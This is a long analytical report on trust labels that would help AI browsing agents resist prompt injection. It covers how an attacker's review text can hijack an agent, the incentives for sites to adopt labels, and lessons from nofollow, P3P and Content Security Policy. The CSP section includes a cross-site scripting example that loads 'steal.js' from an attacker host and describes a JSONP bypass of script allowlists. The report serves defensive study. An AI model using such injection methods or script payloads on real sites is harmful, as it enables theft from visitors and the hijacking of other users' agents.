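In all the tests with hand-written labels, the researchers wrote the labels and treated them as correct, apart from the one deliberate error. A shop's developers would make mistakes, and nobody has measured how many. Like masking, SPIDES treats unlabelled elements on a trusted site as safe. It also treats them as public. Zverev and colleagues acknowledge that keeping labels up to date on changing pages takes work, and they warn that automatic labelling may introduce errors.

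### Why a few errors matter

A model that correctly labels 93% of the strangers' content doesn't stop 93% of attacks, because Eve can choose where to write. If the model recognises review text but overlooks review titles, she can put her instructions in a title. She could find the gap by running the same software on the shop's public pages. The error would recur on every page built from the same template until somebody corrected it.

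Small error rates also add up across a page. Suppose a page has ten groups of untrusted content, and the model has a 6.9% chance of missing each one. If the misses are independent, the chance of at least one is 1 − 0.931<sup>10</sup>, or about 51%. Real errors won't be independent, but the calculation shows how a low average error rate can still leave many pages with a missed group that an attacker could exploit.

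Villa and Tan compared six models' labels with an expert's on 20 page views. With GPT-5.4 nano, the most cautious of the six, 98.7% of the elements that Prismata left available were ones the expert would also have allowed. But Villa and Tan likewise warn that a single wrong label on an important element could still let an attack through. The same model also removed about 17% of the elements the expert would have kept.

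Under masking, one missed label exposes an agent that can use the whole page to Eve's instructions. Prismata's action gate still limits which buttons the agent can press after a mistake, and Eve's text can distort the judgement only for elements beneath that text.

An agent could also combine the two sources and treat an element as untrusted if either the site or the model labels it that way. The model might still recognise the reviews section from its heading after a redesign broke the shop's selector, and the shop's label could cover review titles that the model overlooked. The agent would hide more harmless text, but neither source could make it trust an element that the other had labelled untrusted.

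### Headings and accessibility labels as clues

Agents can infer trust labels as well as they do because developers already describe their pages for other reasons. Accessibility guidelines call for headings that introduce the content below them, and ARIA attributes give names and roles to parts of a page for screen readers. Semantic HTML uses tags such as `nav` and `article` in place of generic containers. Many developers also name classes after the component they style, such as `review-card`. Villa and Tan note that search engines reward some of these habits, so developers have kept them up without considering agents.

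Such markup is common but patchy. WebAIM (2025), an accessibility organisation, tested a million popular home pages and found that 79.4% used ARIA attributes and 80.5% marked at least one region of the page. Only 42.6% marked the main content, and 9.8% had no headings. Shopping sites had the most detectable accessibility errors of any category, averaging 71 per home page against 51 overall. The overall average rose to 56.1 in the next year's survey, according to WebAIM's *tolerating inaccessibility*.

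These error counts are only a rough guide to how well inference would work. The most common error, low-contrast text, doesn't affect a model reading the page's structure. WebAIM also tested only home pages, while most reviews are on product pages. But the figures weaken Zverev and colleagues' argument that trust labels would take little effort because sites already provide similar information for accessibility. In 2025, 94.8% of the home pages had at least one detectable failure to meet the accessibility guidelines.

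Accessibility markup also describes what a part of the page is for, and only hints at who wrote it. An `article` tag might contain the shop's guide to tying a bow tie or a customer's complaint about one. A section named "Featured products" might contain the shop's own listings or those of outside sellers. A screen reader doesn't need to know who wrote each part, so a site can follow every accessibility guideline without making this clear to an agent.

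### Could a site scramble the clues?

A site could make it harder for agents to infer trust labels by disguising its structure. *WebCloak* (Li, Qiu and colleagues) describes a tool that does this to stop AI scrapers from collecting images. It gives tags and attributes random names, so an image might appear in the code as `<xyzq nymmj="image.jpg">`, and a script in the visitor's browser restores the picture. A second layer adds text that people can't see, written to confuse a model or make it refuse. A label based on authorship would mark this text as trusted, as it would other injections by site owners. On 237 saved pages from 50 popular sites, the share of images that leading scraping tools retrieved fell from 88.7% to zero.

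That result combines both layers and concerns image collection, so it doesn't show how scrambled names alone would affect trust labels. Most class names on Booking.com are already meaningless strings such as `ss133neaa`, yet Claude found most of the boundaries from the layout and a few meaningful names. WebCloak hides more, because it also disguises the tags. An agent could use a screenshot, where the heading "Customer reviews" would still be visible, but the screenshot would also include Eve's review.

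An honest shop has little reason to scramble its code. Scrambling could stop Alice's agent from finding the basket button, and a cautious agent might treat the whole page as untrusted. A site that doesn't want agents can more simply block them. *Agent-Targeted Cloaking on the Web* compared what the 10,000 most popular sites sent to an ordinary browser and to an otherwise identical visitor calling itself ChatGPT-User. The declared agent received the same page on 74% of sites, a refusal on 21% and an altered page on 5%. This comparison would miss a site that scrambled its code for every visitor, so it can't show how many sites do that.

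## Do sites and agent makers have reason to cooperate?

An honest bow tie shop has little reason to scramble its pages, but it may not have much reason to label them either. A label on Eve's review has no effect until some agent's software looks for it, and agent makers gain nothing from looking for labels until sites add them, so each side can reasonably wait for the other.

### A model with two sides

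Let *r* be the share of a site's agent visits that come from agents that read trust labels. Let *B* be the yearly benefit to the site if every visiting agent read them, and *c* the yearly cost of writing and maintaining them. The site gains by labelling if

*rB* > *c*

For an agent maker, let *s* be the share of its users' browsing that goes to labelled sites. Let *V* be the yearly benefit to the maker if every site had labels, and *k* the yearly cost of reading them, including the extra model calls that masking needs. The maker gains by reading labels if

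*sV* > *k*

Suppose, purely for illustration, that *B* is $10,000 and *c* is $2,000 for every shop, and that *V* is $20 million and *k* is $3 million for every agent maker. A shop then adds labels once more than 20% of its agent visits come from agents that read them. A maker has its agents read labels once more than 15% of its users' browsing goes to labelled sites.

If nobody takes part, *r* and *s* are both zero. A shop that labels alone spends $2,000 and gains nothing, and a maker that reads labels alone spends $3 million and gains nothing, so nobody starts. If everybody takes part, a shop that drops its labels saves $2,000 but loses $10,000, so nobody leaves. A small disturbance wouldn't change this: if a tenth of browsing moved to unlabelled sites, *s* would fall to 0.9, still far above the 0.15 at which a maker breaks even. Both states are stable, even though each shop is $8,000 a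 year better off when everybody takes part, and each maker $17 million better off.

A large early adopter can move everyone from the first state to the second. Suppose one agent maker starts reading labels before any site has them:

| First maker's share of agent visits | Yearly benefit to a shop that labels | What happens |
|---|---|---|
| 5% | $500 | Shops don't label |
| 15% | $1,500 | Shops don't label |
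| 25% | $2,500 | Shops label, and the other makers then start reading |

The maker with 25% of visits still loses $3 million a year until the shops respond. If the shops take two years, it will have lost $6 million before it starts to gain $17 million a year. Its rivals can wait and then use the same labels without that early loss, so every maker would prefer another maker to go first.

Large sites could also start the process. Half of all internet traffic goes to 3,000 domains, so the busiest 900 must carry at least 15% of all traffic. If agents browse roughly where people do, those 900 would be enough to meet the makers' 15% threshold in this example. A company that runs the software behind many shops could label all their reviews by changing one template.

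Unlike these identical shops, real sites differ from one another. A forum has a lot to gain from labels, but a bank's website that shows no text from strangers has nothing to gain. If labelling cost a shop $100, it would pay off once 1% of agent visits came from agents that read the labels. If labels are cheap, they could spread among sites even if agent makers don't have their agents read them, much as automatically generated llms.txt files have.

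### Getting past the tipping point

Ozment and Schechter (2006), in *Bootstrapping the Adoption of Internet Security Protocols*, analysed this kind of standoff for security technologies. They model a single group of users, in which the benefit of adopting, *B*(*x*), grows with the fraction *x* who have already adopted. A user adopts when *B*(*x*) exceeds the cost. If the benefit starts below the cost, nobody goes first, even when a subset of users would all gain by adopting together. The tipping point is the level of adoption at which the benefit overtakes the cost.

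Ozment and Schechter describe six ways to reach it, each of which has a possible counterpart for trust labels:

| Approach | What it might look like for trust labels |
|---|---|
| Global mandate | A law requires every site to label strangers' text |
| Partial mandate | Card companies require labels from shops that take orders from agents |
| Bundling with something useful | Shops adopt WebMCP to win sales and fill in its untrusted-content hint at the same time |
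| Adoption within one organisation | Microsoft labels GitHub's pages and has its own Copilot agents read the labels |
| Coordination | Several agent makers promise to start reading labels on the same date |
| Subsidy | A browser maker pays for plugins that label reviews automatically |

Adoption looks easiest within one organisation, because a company that owns both a site and an agent doesn't have to wait for anyone else. Competitors could plausibly coordinate too, since four of them quickly backed a shared training opt-out. However, that opt-out only requires looking up a rule in robots.txt, which is much simpler than masking parts of a page.

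Ozment and Schechter identify a further difficulty for technologies that prove who sent a message. If Alice receives an unsigned email that claims to come from a colleague, it is a forgery if the colleague signs every message, but it may be genuine if the colleague has never adopted signatures. Alice can reject all unsigned mail and miss messages from everyone who hasn't adopted signatures, or accept it and lose most of the protection.

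Unlabelled text on a web page is ambiguous in the same way. On a cooperating site, a missing label means that the owner vouches for the text, but on a passive honest site it means nothing. Ozment and Schechter's remedy is a secure way for a domain to announce that it has adopted the technology. A site could similarly declare that it labels all text written by strangers. But a hostile site could make the same declaration, so the agent would still need a reason to believe the site's labels.

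Labels have one advantage over signed email, which is that an agent doesn't have to refuse unlabelled pages. It can infer labels or rely on its other defences. But *V*, the value that labels add to what an agent can already do, shrinks as agents get better at defending themselves. If *V* fell from $20 million to $5 million, a maker would need 60% of its users' browsing to go to labelled sites before it gained anything.

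### Who pays and who benefits

The model also assumes that shops benefit enough to cover their costs, which may be wrong. If Eve's review hijacks Alice's agent, Alice loses money and the agent's maker loses some of her trust. The shop might face a complaint or lose a customer, but only if somebody traces the attack to its page. If the full benefit to the shop were $1,500 a year, it wouldn't pay $2,000 for labels even when every agent read them, so universal labelling would no longer be stable.

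In *What Makes for a Successful Protocol?* (IETF RFC 5218), Thaler and Aboba (2008) found from case studies that protocols succeed most easily when the organisations that must make a change also gain most from it. They also found that a protocol has a better chance if early adopters benefit before the rest of the internet adopts it, and if it works when only one end of a connection changes. Trust labels do poorly on all three counts. An agent-side defence does well because the agent maker pays for it, the maker's users benefit, and no website has to change.

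One remedy is to give sites a benefit that doesn't depend on agents. If labelling brought a shop *h* dollars a year regardless of who visited, the shop would label when *rB* + *h* > *c*. With *h* at $1,500 and the other figures as they were originally, the threshold falls from 20% of agent visits to 5%. *Build agent-friendly websites*, on Google's web.dev, makes a similar case for stable layouts and clearly marked buttons, which it says help people as well as agents. A `data-untrusted` attribute is different because people never see it. It might still pay for itself early at a shop whose own customer-service chatbot reads reviews and needs protection from Eve.

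Agent makers could also reward sites for labelling content, for instance by having agents ask Alice for fewer confirmations on labelled sites. That would raise *B*, but it would also reward sites that add labels without checking their accuracy.

Thaler and Aboba suggest allowing an average protocol five to ten years before declaring it a failure. The labelling scheme that Nikolić and colleagues proposed is less than six months old, so its current lack of users is weak evidence against it.

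### The W3C debate about honesty

Even labels that recoup their cost could mislead agents if sites wrote them dishonestly. Web developers and browser engineers argued about this at a W3C session on 12 November 2025. The draft minutes, W3C's *Agentic Browsing and the Web's Security Model* (2025), list most speakers only by handle. Two, mnot and dveditz, appear to be Mark Nottingham and Daniel Veditz, both veterans of web standards work.

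One speaker suggested that browsers could prevent agents from taking in certain content at all. A participant with the handle AramZS liked the idea as a developer but said, according to the minutes, that "incentives don't align." AramZS pointed out that a developer for a publisher that doesn't want to be crawled would want to mark all content as untrusted and all ads as trusted. An agent that relied on those labels would take in the ads but not the article.

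Nottingham argued that hints still help defenders more than attackers, because an attacker needs to find only one sensitive item on a page and can do so without help, while a defender must protect all of them. Veditz objected that a browser can't tell a legitimate site's honest hints from an illegitimate site's malicious ones. Nottingham replied that this isn't a problem when a hint only steers agents away from something. Veditz disagreed, because a site could steer an agent away from the information its user wanted.

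Veditz then described how a shop could mark the real price, which people can see, as unsafe and offer agents a "safe" button, invisible to people, that charges more. He expected a public relations disaster if a large, well-known company were caught doing this, but could imagine a bunch of small shops trying it.

Nottingham and Veditz were mostly answering different questions. Nottingham considered whether labels help an outside attacker such as Eve, and his argument holds if the shop is honest. Veditz considered a shop that uses labels against its own customers.

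Other participants thought agents might have good reason to ignore hints. One, tomayac, gave the example of an accessibility agent that has to read information marked as sensitive to complete its user's task. Another, kbabbitt, noted that someone planning a trip might want an agent to notice an advertisement for a discounted flight, but not one claiming that their computer has a virus.

A participant called mt_hates_irc objected to showing an agent anything different from what a person sees, because nobody could then diagnose attacks on the agent. Masking creates this difference when it replaces reviews with placeholders. The masking software could record each hidden passage for investigators, but a person watching the agent would still see a different page from the one the agent receives.

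### Which sites want agents

A site's reasons to label honestly depend on what it wants from agents. The last column below lists temptations, since too few sites write trust labels for anyone to have measured how often they lie:

| Kind of site | What it wants | What it has reason to label honestly | What it might label falsely |
|---|---|---|---|
| Shop that wants agent customers | Sales | Reviews and outside sellers' listings | Its own fees and cheaper options, as untrusted |
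| Platform that hosts strangers' text | Safe users, and sometimes payment for data | Posts, comments and usernames | Paid listings, as trusted |
| Publisher that loses visits | Readers, advertising income or licence fees | Readers' comments | Articles as untrusted, advertisements as trusted |
| Rival of the agent's maker | Customers for its own service | Whatever its own agent reads | Anything that makes the other agent less useful |

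Some shops are already adapting their sites to agents. *The Structured Surface*, a newsletter from the vendor TinyFish, lists Expedia, Etsy, Instacart and Target among the companies testing WebMCP. These companies would also be the most likely to label reviews, because an agent that Eve hijacks may never finish its purchase.

Other sites turned agents away in the autumn of 2026. Slashdot's *Websites Are Closing Their Doors to AI Agents* (2026), which excerpts an October report by The Verge, describes several motives. JPMorgan Chase and Charles Schwab blocked agents from customers' accounts because of security concerns. Yelp, whose business depends on user reviews, admitted only agents that paid for its data licensing program. Delta Air Lines stopped agents from booking tickets. Amazon said that continued access by Muse, Meta's assistant, violated its policies. Meta then reached agreements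 with retailers including Walmart, Gap and Best Buy that let Muse shop on their sites, and Shopify opened its network of storefronts to agents.

Meta responded to the blocks by arguing that a site that turns away an agent also turns away the customer using it (Neely, 2026, *Websites are closing their doors to AI agents (The Verge)*). This argument should persuade a small shop more than Amazon, whose customers may return and buy without the agent.

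Many publishers have a weaker reason to admit agents, because an agent can take an article's content without anyone seeing the advertisements. Southern (2026), in *More News Sites Default To Blocking AI Crawlers*, reported in June that Reuters and Time blocked AI bots by default and admitted only approved ones. In September, Zyte's *Four in 10 sites block AI bots with robots.txt* reported that nearly 40% of top sites were closed to AI crawlers that obey robots.txt. That figure covers crawlers, so it doesn't show how many of the sites would refuse a shopping agent.

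Some sites block agents without meaning to. Parvez (2026), in *Why some websites are blocking AI agents from accessing the web*, attributes some blocks to sites mistaking agents for scrapers and others to deliberate bans. Owners who never check Cloudflare's new default settings can also block agents by accident, so Digital Matters' *AI Shopping Agents Are Getting Blocked* (2026) advises charities to look at their donation pages. Cloudflare's *Building an open Agentic Internet* describes a partial remedy, developed with Mozilla, Google, Microsoft and Shopify. A site that already knows a customer could issue an anonymous token, which the customer's agent would show to other sites as evidence that it is legitimate.

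### Amazon and its rivals' agents

Amazon sells its own shopping services, so an outside agent brings it orders but also competes with it for customers' attention. *The Coming Fight to Define the Agentic Web*, from the American think tank AEI, reports that Amazon repeatedly changed its robots.txt to exclude AI crawlers and agents, and that eBay banned "buy-for-me agents" in its user agreement. Meta has been on both sides of such disputes, and the European Commission opened an antitrust investigation into it over WhatsApp rules that restrict other companies' chatbots.

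In November 2025 Amazon sued Perplexity, whose Comet browser includes a shopping agent. According to The Fashion Law's *Can Companies Use Anti-Hacking Laws to Stop AI Shopping Agents?*, Comet takes screenshots of a customer's browser and sends them to Perplexity's servers, which return instructions for navigating Amazon. Amazon claimed this was unauthorised access under US federal and Californian computer-crime law. Bloomberg Law's *Ninth Circuit Weighs AI Shopping Fraud Case* (2026) reports that Amazon also complained that Comet didn't disclose when an agent was shopping for a person.

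A district court temporarily barred Perplexity's agent from Amazon's site, but a federal appeals court lifted the ban on 4 August 2026. Cooley's *Ninth Circuit Rules on AI Agent ‘Access’ to Third-Party Websites Under CFAA* (2026) explains that the appeals court held Amazon was unlikely to win its computer-access claims because the customer, not Perplexity, had accessed Amazon's computers. MediaPost's *Appeals Court Sides Against Amazon, Lifts Perplexity Ban* (2026) quotes the court's concern that a ban "would impair consumer choice". The appeals court left its ruling in place in September.

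Ropes & Gray's *Tool or Intruder* (2026) stresses that the court ruled on the facts before it. The ruling doesn't require Amazon to make its site work for outside agents, and Amazon moved against Muse soon afterwards. If lawsuits become less effective, a site that objects to agents has more reason to rely on technical barriers or on the content of its pages.

Trust labels can help even agents that don't disclose themselves. An agent that expects a site to block it has a reason to hide, and then it can't receive anything the site reserves for agents that identify themselves. But a label in the page's HTML reaches every visitor, so the bow tie shop's mark on Eve's review would protect an agent even if it hid.

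### Sites that write instructions against agents

Some site owners already use their pages to obstruct AI systems. Khodayari and colleagues confirmed injections on 2,042 hosts. Of these, 1,795 carried text meant to protect personal information or copyrighted material, and 1,864 carried text meant to disrupt AI systems, so at least 1,617 carried both. Many of these owners apparently tried to protect their content by spoiling the AI systems' output.

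Instructions meant to protect personal information appeared on 1,501 hosts, while those meant to protect copyright appeared on 357, which Khodayari and colleagues think fits larger content providers. They conclude that these instructions cause friction without reliably controlling agents.

These owners would have little reason to write helpful labels, and there are enough of them to make Veditz's worry about sites acting against agents seem realistic. However, two of the three sources in this combined dataset were searched specifically for injections, so we can't tell from the counts what share of all sites behaves this way.

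### Labels that work on selfish sites

An agent can allow for a site's motives by deciding in advance what each kind of label may change:

| Effect of the label | What a selfish site could gain | When an agent can rely on it |
|---|---|---|
| The text can't give the agent instructions | Almost nothing | On any site |
| The agent can't see the text | It could hide a fee, a lower price or an article | When it has a way to check what is hidden |
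| The agent must ask its user first | It could make the agent tiresome to use | When the maker limits how often this happens |
| The agent trusts the text or tool more | It could steer or hijack the agent | Only when it has independent reason to trust the site |

The rule in the first row is the most robust. If a publisher marked every article as untrusted, an agent following that rule would ignore any instructions in the articles but could still summarise them. Marking its advertisements as "trusted" would have no effect. A shop would gain nothing by marking its prices as untrusted, because the agent could still read and compare them.

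Masking enforces this rule by hiding the text, but hiding it moves the label into the second row and makes Veditz's trick possible. A compiled program avoids the problem because it can still compare prices marked as untrusted. An agent that uses masking could have the quarantined model check hidden elements near the checkout for prices or fees, and show Alice the result before she pays.

A site that wants agents to leave has little reason to use false labels, because blocking agents is easier. A shop that wants Alice's money has more reason, because it could mark its restocking fee as untrusted to hide it from her agent. But the false label would be in the page, where anyone who loaded the same version could find it. A browser maker could scan popular shops for fees and prices marked as untrusted, and stop hiding marked text on shops that abused the label.

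## What earlier web standards show about uptake

Website owners have often had to decide whether to publish signals for software to read. Some standards for doing this, such as robots.txt, spread to nearly every site. Others stalled for a decade or came to contain many false statements. The ten standards below differ in who acted on the signal and what its senders stood to gain. These two factors also determine the outcome in the adoption model.

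| Standard | What someone has to publish | Who acts on it | Reason to take part |
|---|---|---|---|
| schema.org (2011) | Coded descriptions of a page's contents | Search engines | Richer search listings |
| rel=nofollow (2005) | A mark on links the site doesn't vouch for | Search engines | Less reward for comment spam |
| ads.txt (2017) | A list of companies allowed to sell the site's ad space | Advertisers' buying software | Advertising revenue |
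| HTTPS (1990s) | A certificate for encrypted connections | Browsers | No security warnings |
| DMARC (2012) | A rule for handling forged email | Mail services | Delivery of the site's own email |
| Global Privacy Control (2020) | A request not to sell the user's data | Websites | California law |
| Do Not Track (2009) | A request not to track the user | Websites | None |
| Keywords meta tag (1990s) | Words describing the page | Search engines | Higher ranking |
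| P3P (2002) | A coded privacy policy | Internet Explorer | Cookies that the browser accepts |
| Content Security Policy (2010) | Rules for which scripts may run | Browsers | Protection from planted code |

The user's browser sends the two privacy requests and the website decides whether to obey them, which is the reverse of how the other standards work.

### Rewards from a dominant reader

Google, Microsoft and Yahoo launched schema.org in June 2011 as a shared vocabulary for describing what a page contains. The bow tie shop might use it to label a product's price as $45 and its average rating as 4.6 stars. A search engine may then show the price and stars beside the shop's link, which can draw clicks from plainer links nearby. In 2015, engineers who ran the project reported that 31.3% of pages in a sample of ten billion used the vocabulary, up from 22% a year earlier. By 2024, over 45 million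 domains used it, according to the project's own site.

The reward also gave sites a reason to exaggerate. Google requires the markup to match what visitors can see, and it can remove the richer listing from a site that breaks this rule. In 2019 it stopped showing stars for ratings that businesses published about themselves. These checks only protect Google's results, so an agent that reads the markup straight from the page can still be misled, as the fake DeBank site's metadata showed.

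The closest ancestor of a trust label is `rel="nofollow"`. By 2005 spammers were filling blog comments with links, because search engines counted each link as a recommendation. Google, Yahoo and Microsoft agreed that January to give no ranking credit to a link marked like this:

```
<a href="https://eve.example" rel="nofollow">cheap ties</a>
```

A blog's owner could thus disown links that strangers had posted. Most owners never had to learn how, because WordPress and other blogging software added the mark to comment links automatically. By the early 2020s, roughly three in ten home pages used the mark.

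Comment spam continued anyway, since posting cost spammers almost nothing and a link could still bring visitors. The search engines benefited more clearly, because they could discount the marked links. Some site owners then used the mark selfishly, putting it on links to their own minor pages so that more ranking credit would go to the pages they wanted to promote. Google changed its calculation to remove the advantage, and the standard survived.

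In 2019 Google introduced a more specific value, `ugc`, for links in user-generated content, and WordPress began adding it to comment links the same year. Many blogs already mark strangers' links this way, and an agent could use the mark as a clue to who wrote the surrounding comment. Comments without links don't have the mark, but they can carry instructions just as well.

Publishers had a financial incentive to adopt ads.txt. Fraudsters had been selling advertising space that they falsely claimed was on well-known sites. In 2017 the IAB Tech Lab, the advertising industry's standards body, proposed that each publisher list its authorised sellers in a text file at the root of its domain. An advertiser's software can compare a seller's account number with the list before buying space. Within months, Google announced that if a site had published a file, its main buying tool would not buy that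 site's space from unlisted sellers.

Bashir and colleagues at Northeastern University followed the standard for 15 months and reported in 2019 that, among the 100,000 most popular sites, over 60% of publishers selling through automated auctions had adopted it. Publishers had good reason to keep the file accurate, because leaving out a legitimate seller could cost them sales. The publishers who maintained the file also benefited from it, because they recovered some of the income that fraudsters had been taking.

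### Pressure from gatekeepers

HTTPS encrypts the connection between a browser and a site. To offer it, a site needs a certificate, which for years cost money and had to be renewed manually. Let's Encrypt, a non-profit certificate authority, began issuing free certificates automatically in late 2015. Meanwhile, browser makers put pressure on sites without HTTPS by warning their visitors. Chrome labelled unencrypted pages that asked for passwords or card numbers "Not secure" from January 2017, and extended the label to all unencrypted pages in July 2018.

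Report URI's *10 years of watching the web* gives results from daily crawls of the million most popular sites. The number using HTTPS rose from 62,043 in 2015 to 658,038 in June 2026, or 80.3% of the sites that answered. The *Security* chapter of HTTP Archive's 2025 Web Almanac, a yearly survey, reports HTTPS on 97.3% of mobile home pages. The two projects use different lists of sites, and Report URI counts only sites that redirect visitors to the encrypted version.

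Free certificates and browser warnings arrived so close together that their effects are hard to separate. Let's Encrypt supplied certificates to 52.6% of the sites in the Almanac, which suggests that cheap automation mattered, though some of those sites would otherwise have paid for a certificate. By comparison, use of the older Extended Validation certificates, which require a company to prove its legal identity, fell by 51% to 4,186 sites. Report URI attributes this to the manual work involved. But Chrome and Firefox also stopped showing the company's verified name in the address bar in 2019, so buyers lost the visible benefit.

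Mail services applied similar pressure with DMARC. A domain's owner publishes a record to tell mail services how to treat messages that claim to come from the domain but fail authentication. The owner can ask them to reject the messages, put them in the spam folder, or deliver them as usual and send reports. In October 2023 Google and Yahoo announced that bulk senders would need such a record from February 2024. Gmail defined bulk senders as those sending 5,000 or more messages a day to its users.

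EasyDMARC, which sells DMARC services, found valid DMARC records on 27.2% of 1.8 million leading domains in 2023 and on 47.7% in 2025. Google reported a 65% fall in unauthenticated messages to Gmail in 2024. In Report URI's June 2026 crawl, 398,597 sites had a DMARC record, but 51.4% of those records were set only to request reports. The mail services' rule accepts this weakest setting, so many senders could comply without blocking any forged mail. Similarly, if agent makers favoured any shop whose pages contained a `data-untrusted` attribute, many shops might add only one label.

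### The same kind of request with and without a law

Do Not Track and Global Privacy Control are technically almost identical. In each, the browser adds a short line to its requests, `DNT: 1` or `Sec-GPC: 1`, to state the user's privacy preference.

The major browsers supported Do Not Track by 2012, but a W3C working group that ran from 2011 to 2019 never settled what websites had to do in response. Advertisers objected when Microsoft turned the setting on by default, because the signal no longer showed that a person had chosen it. A 2018 survey by the search company DuckDuckGo found that about 23% of American adults had enabled the setting. Nearly all large sites ignored the signal, and Mozilla removed the setting from Firefox in 2025.

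Global Privacy Control began in 2020, when Californians already had a legal right to stop businesses selling their data. The state's regulations require the businesses they cover to treat the signal as a valid opt-out. In 2022 the cosmetics chain Sephora paid $1.2 million to settle claims that included a failure to honor the signal. The retailer Tractor Supply paid $1.35 million in 2025 in a case that also covered the signal. Another California law requires browsers to offer a setting that sends an opt-out signal from January 2027.

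These cases show that ignoring the signal can be expensive, but they don't measure how many sites comply. The law also wasn't the only difference between Do Not Track and Global Privacy Control. Nobody had defined what companies should stop doing when they received a Do Not Track signal, whereas a statute had already described the right that users invoke through Global Privacy Control. Honoring either signal also meant giving up income. A shop that labels Eve's review gives up very little, so a law might matter less for trust labels than it did for these privacy signals.

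### Labels that favoured their authors

In the 1990s, website owners could add a hidden list of keywords, called the keywords meta tag, to help search engines classify a page. Visitors didn't see the list, so owners could include popular words unrelated to the page. AltaVista, once a leading search engine, stopped using the tag in 2002, and Google confirmed in 2009 that it ignored the tag for ranking. Search engines lost little by ignoring it because the visible text and links from other sites were better evidence of what a page was about.

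The Platform for Privacy Preferences (P3P) deserved to be taken more seriously. The W3C published it in 2002 so that browsers could compare a site's privacy practices with the user's preferences. A site was supposed to publish a full policy in a coded format, and could add a compact version summarising its use of cookies in three- and four-letter tokens. Regulators from several countries agreed that year that a P3P policy was a legally binding statement to consumers.

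Internet Explorer, which then had about 90% of the browser market, read the compact version. By default, it rejected cookies from third parties that sent no compact policy or an unsatisfactory one. Sites that relied on third-party cookies therefore had an immediate reason to publish a policy, and an equally strong reason to publish one the browser would accept.

As early as January 2002, Cranor (2002), who had led work on the standard, objected on a W3C mailing list to a proposed workaround. It combined a policy that would get through the filter with an extra token that meant, in effect, "just kidding" and that the browser would ignore. Cranor warned that American regulators would probably consider this deceptive.

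Leon, Cranor and colleagues (2010), in *Token Attempt*, measured the result. They collected compact policies from 33,139 websites and checked them for invalid codes, missing codes and contradictions, without testing whether the policies described the sites' actual behaviour. They found:

| Measurement | Result |
|---|---|
| Compact policies with at least one detectable error | 11,176 (33.7%) |
| Compact policies without the full policy that P3P required | 79% |
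| Invalid compact policies that left cookies unblocked in Internet Explorer | 98% |
| Policies with errors among the 48 most popular sites that had one | 21 |

Many errors were innocent, such as swapped letters. Companies with several sites repeated their mistakes, and counting domains instead of sites lowers the error rate to 23.7%. But thousands of sites used identical invalid policies that people had recommended for getting around the filter. The browser's rules helped these sites, because a policy that left out the categories of data a site collected counted as a claim that it collected none.

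Full P3P policies were no better than compact ones. Leon and colleagues summarise earlier work that found syntax errors in 73% of 14,720 full policies. Researchers also compared 21 full policies with the same sites' written policies, and all 21 contradicted them. Only about 10% of 5,739 sites tested in 2003 used P3P. By 2010 the Federal Trade Commission, the American consumer protection agency, had never acted against a false machine-readable policy. In 2012 Microsoft complained that Google was sending a compact policy that Internet Explorer accepted even though its text stated that it was not a P3P policy.

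A dominant browser read P3P statements, sites had a direct reward for providing them, and the statements had some legal force in theory. Yet the browser relaxed its protection based on statements it couldn't check. A false `readOnlyHint` on a shop's purchase tool would exploit the same weakness. The nofollow mark fared better largely because it could only reduce the credit a link received.

### How Content Security Policy works

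Researchers who want sites to label untrusted content usually point to Content Security Policy (CSP). It deals with cross-site scripting, the older attack that Villa and Tan compare with prompt injection.

Suppose Eve's review of the bow tie contains code as well as words:

```
Lovely tie! <script src="https://eve.example/steal.js"></script>
```

If the shop copies this into its page unchanged, every visitor's browser will run Eve's program as though the shop had written it. The program could read Alice's address from the page or place an order from her account. The main defence is for the shop's software to convert the angle brackets into harmless characters, so that visitors see the code as text. But a large site displays strangers' text in hundreds of places, and the site is vulnerable if a developer forgets the conversion in any one of them.

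CSP limits the damage when that happens. The shop's server sends a header with each page, listing the sources from which scripts may come:

```
Content-Security-Policy: script-src 'self' https://analytics.example
```

Here the browser will run scripts from the shop's own domain and from one analytics company. It blocks Eve's script because `eve.example` isn't on the list. It also blocks inline scripts, whose code sits directly in the page, because it can't distinguish the shop's from Eve's. A shop that depends on inline scripts can allow them by adding the keyword `unsafe-inline`, but that also allows Eve's.

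A newer kind of policy uses a nonce, a random value that the server generates afresh for each page. The server puts the nonce in the header and on every script that the shop intends to run:

```
Content-Security-Policy: script-src 'nonce-Kx82mQ'

<script nonce="Kx82mQ" src="/basket.js"></script>
```

Eve writes her review before the server chooses the value, so she can't include it in her script tag.

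### A decade of weak policies

Weichselbaum, Spagnuolo and colleagues (2016), in *CSP Is Dead, Long Live CSP!*, searched about 106 billion pages in a Google index. They found policies on 0.16% of a billion hostnames. About a million of the 1.7 million hostnames with a policy belonged to five e-commerce applications that reused the same few, so the team reduced the collection to 26,011 distinct policies and tested those:

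| Policies tested | Number | Share an attacker could bypass |
|---|---|---|
| All distinct policies | 26,011 | 94.72% |
| Enforced policies meant to control scripts | 22,425 | 94.68% |
| Those without obvious flaws, such as `unsafe-inline` | 2,437 | 51.05% |

Content Security Policy gave no protection from cross-site scripting on 99.34% of the hostnames that used it. The main cause was `unsafe-inline` without a nonce, which appeared in 87.63% of the policies meant to control scripts.

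The careful policies often failed because of the domains they approved. Suppose `analytics.example` lets a site request data and name the function that will receive it. The request ends in `callback=showChart`, and the server replies with a script that begins `showChart(`. Eve can request the same address with her own code in place of `showChart`. The server copies her code into its reply, and the browser runs it because the reply comes from an approved domain. The address is harmless until some site's security depends on the whole domain, so the domain's owner has no reason to remove it.

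The median policy listed 12 hosts, and the researchers could bypass 94.8% of policies of that length. They found a bypass on 14 of the 15 most commonly approved domains. Seven of the ten worst domains belonged to Google, where the researchers worked. They concluded that nobody could keep a long list of approved domains secure in practice and recommended nonces instead.

Uptake has grown a great deal since then. HTTP Archive found CSP on 21.9% of sites in 2025, up from 18.5% the year before. Report URI counted it on about 1,400 popular sites in 2016 and on 170,057 (20.8%) in June 2026. However, sites mostly use CSP for other purposes. The two most common instructions tell browsers to upgrade insecure requests and to control which other sites may embed the page, and each appears in at least half of CSP headers.

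HTTP Archive found `unsafe-inline` in 92% of policies that control scripts. This figure overstates the weakness, because modern browsers ignore the keyword when the policy also contains a nonce, and some sites keep it only for old browsers. But only about 20% of these policies contained a nonce, so at least 72% had the keyword without one, although a few of those may disable it by other means. Report URI's lower figure of 46.8% covers every policy, including those that don't restrict scripts.

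Companies with large security teams have done better with Content Security Policy (CSP). Report URI's *Client-Side Security Reporting* (2026) lists GitHub, PayPal and several Google services among the sites that enforce a policy. It reports that cross-site scripting's share of Google's payments to outside bug hunters fell from 30% in 2018 to 4.1% in 2023. Report URI sells tools for managing these policies, and Google improved other defences over the same years, so CSP may explain only part of the drop.

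### Why sites found it hard

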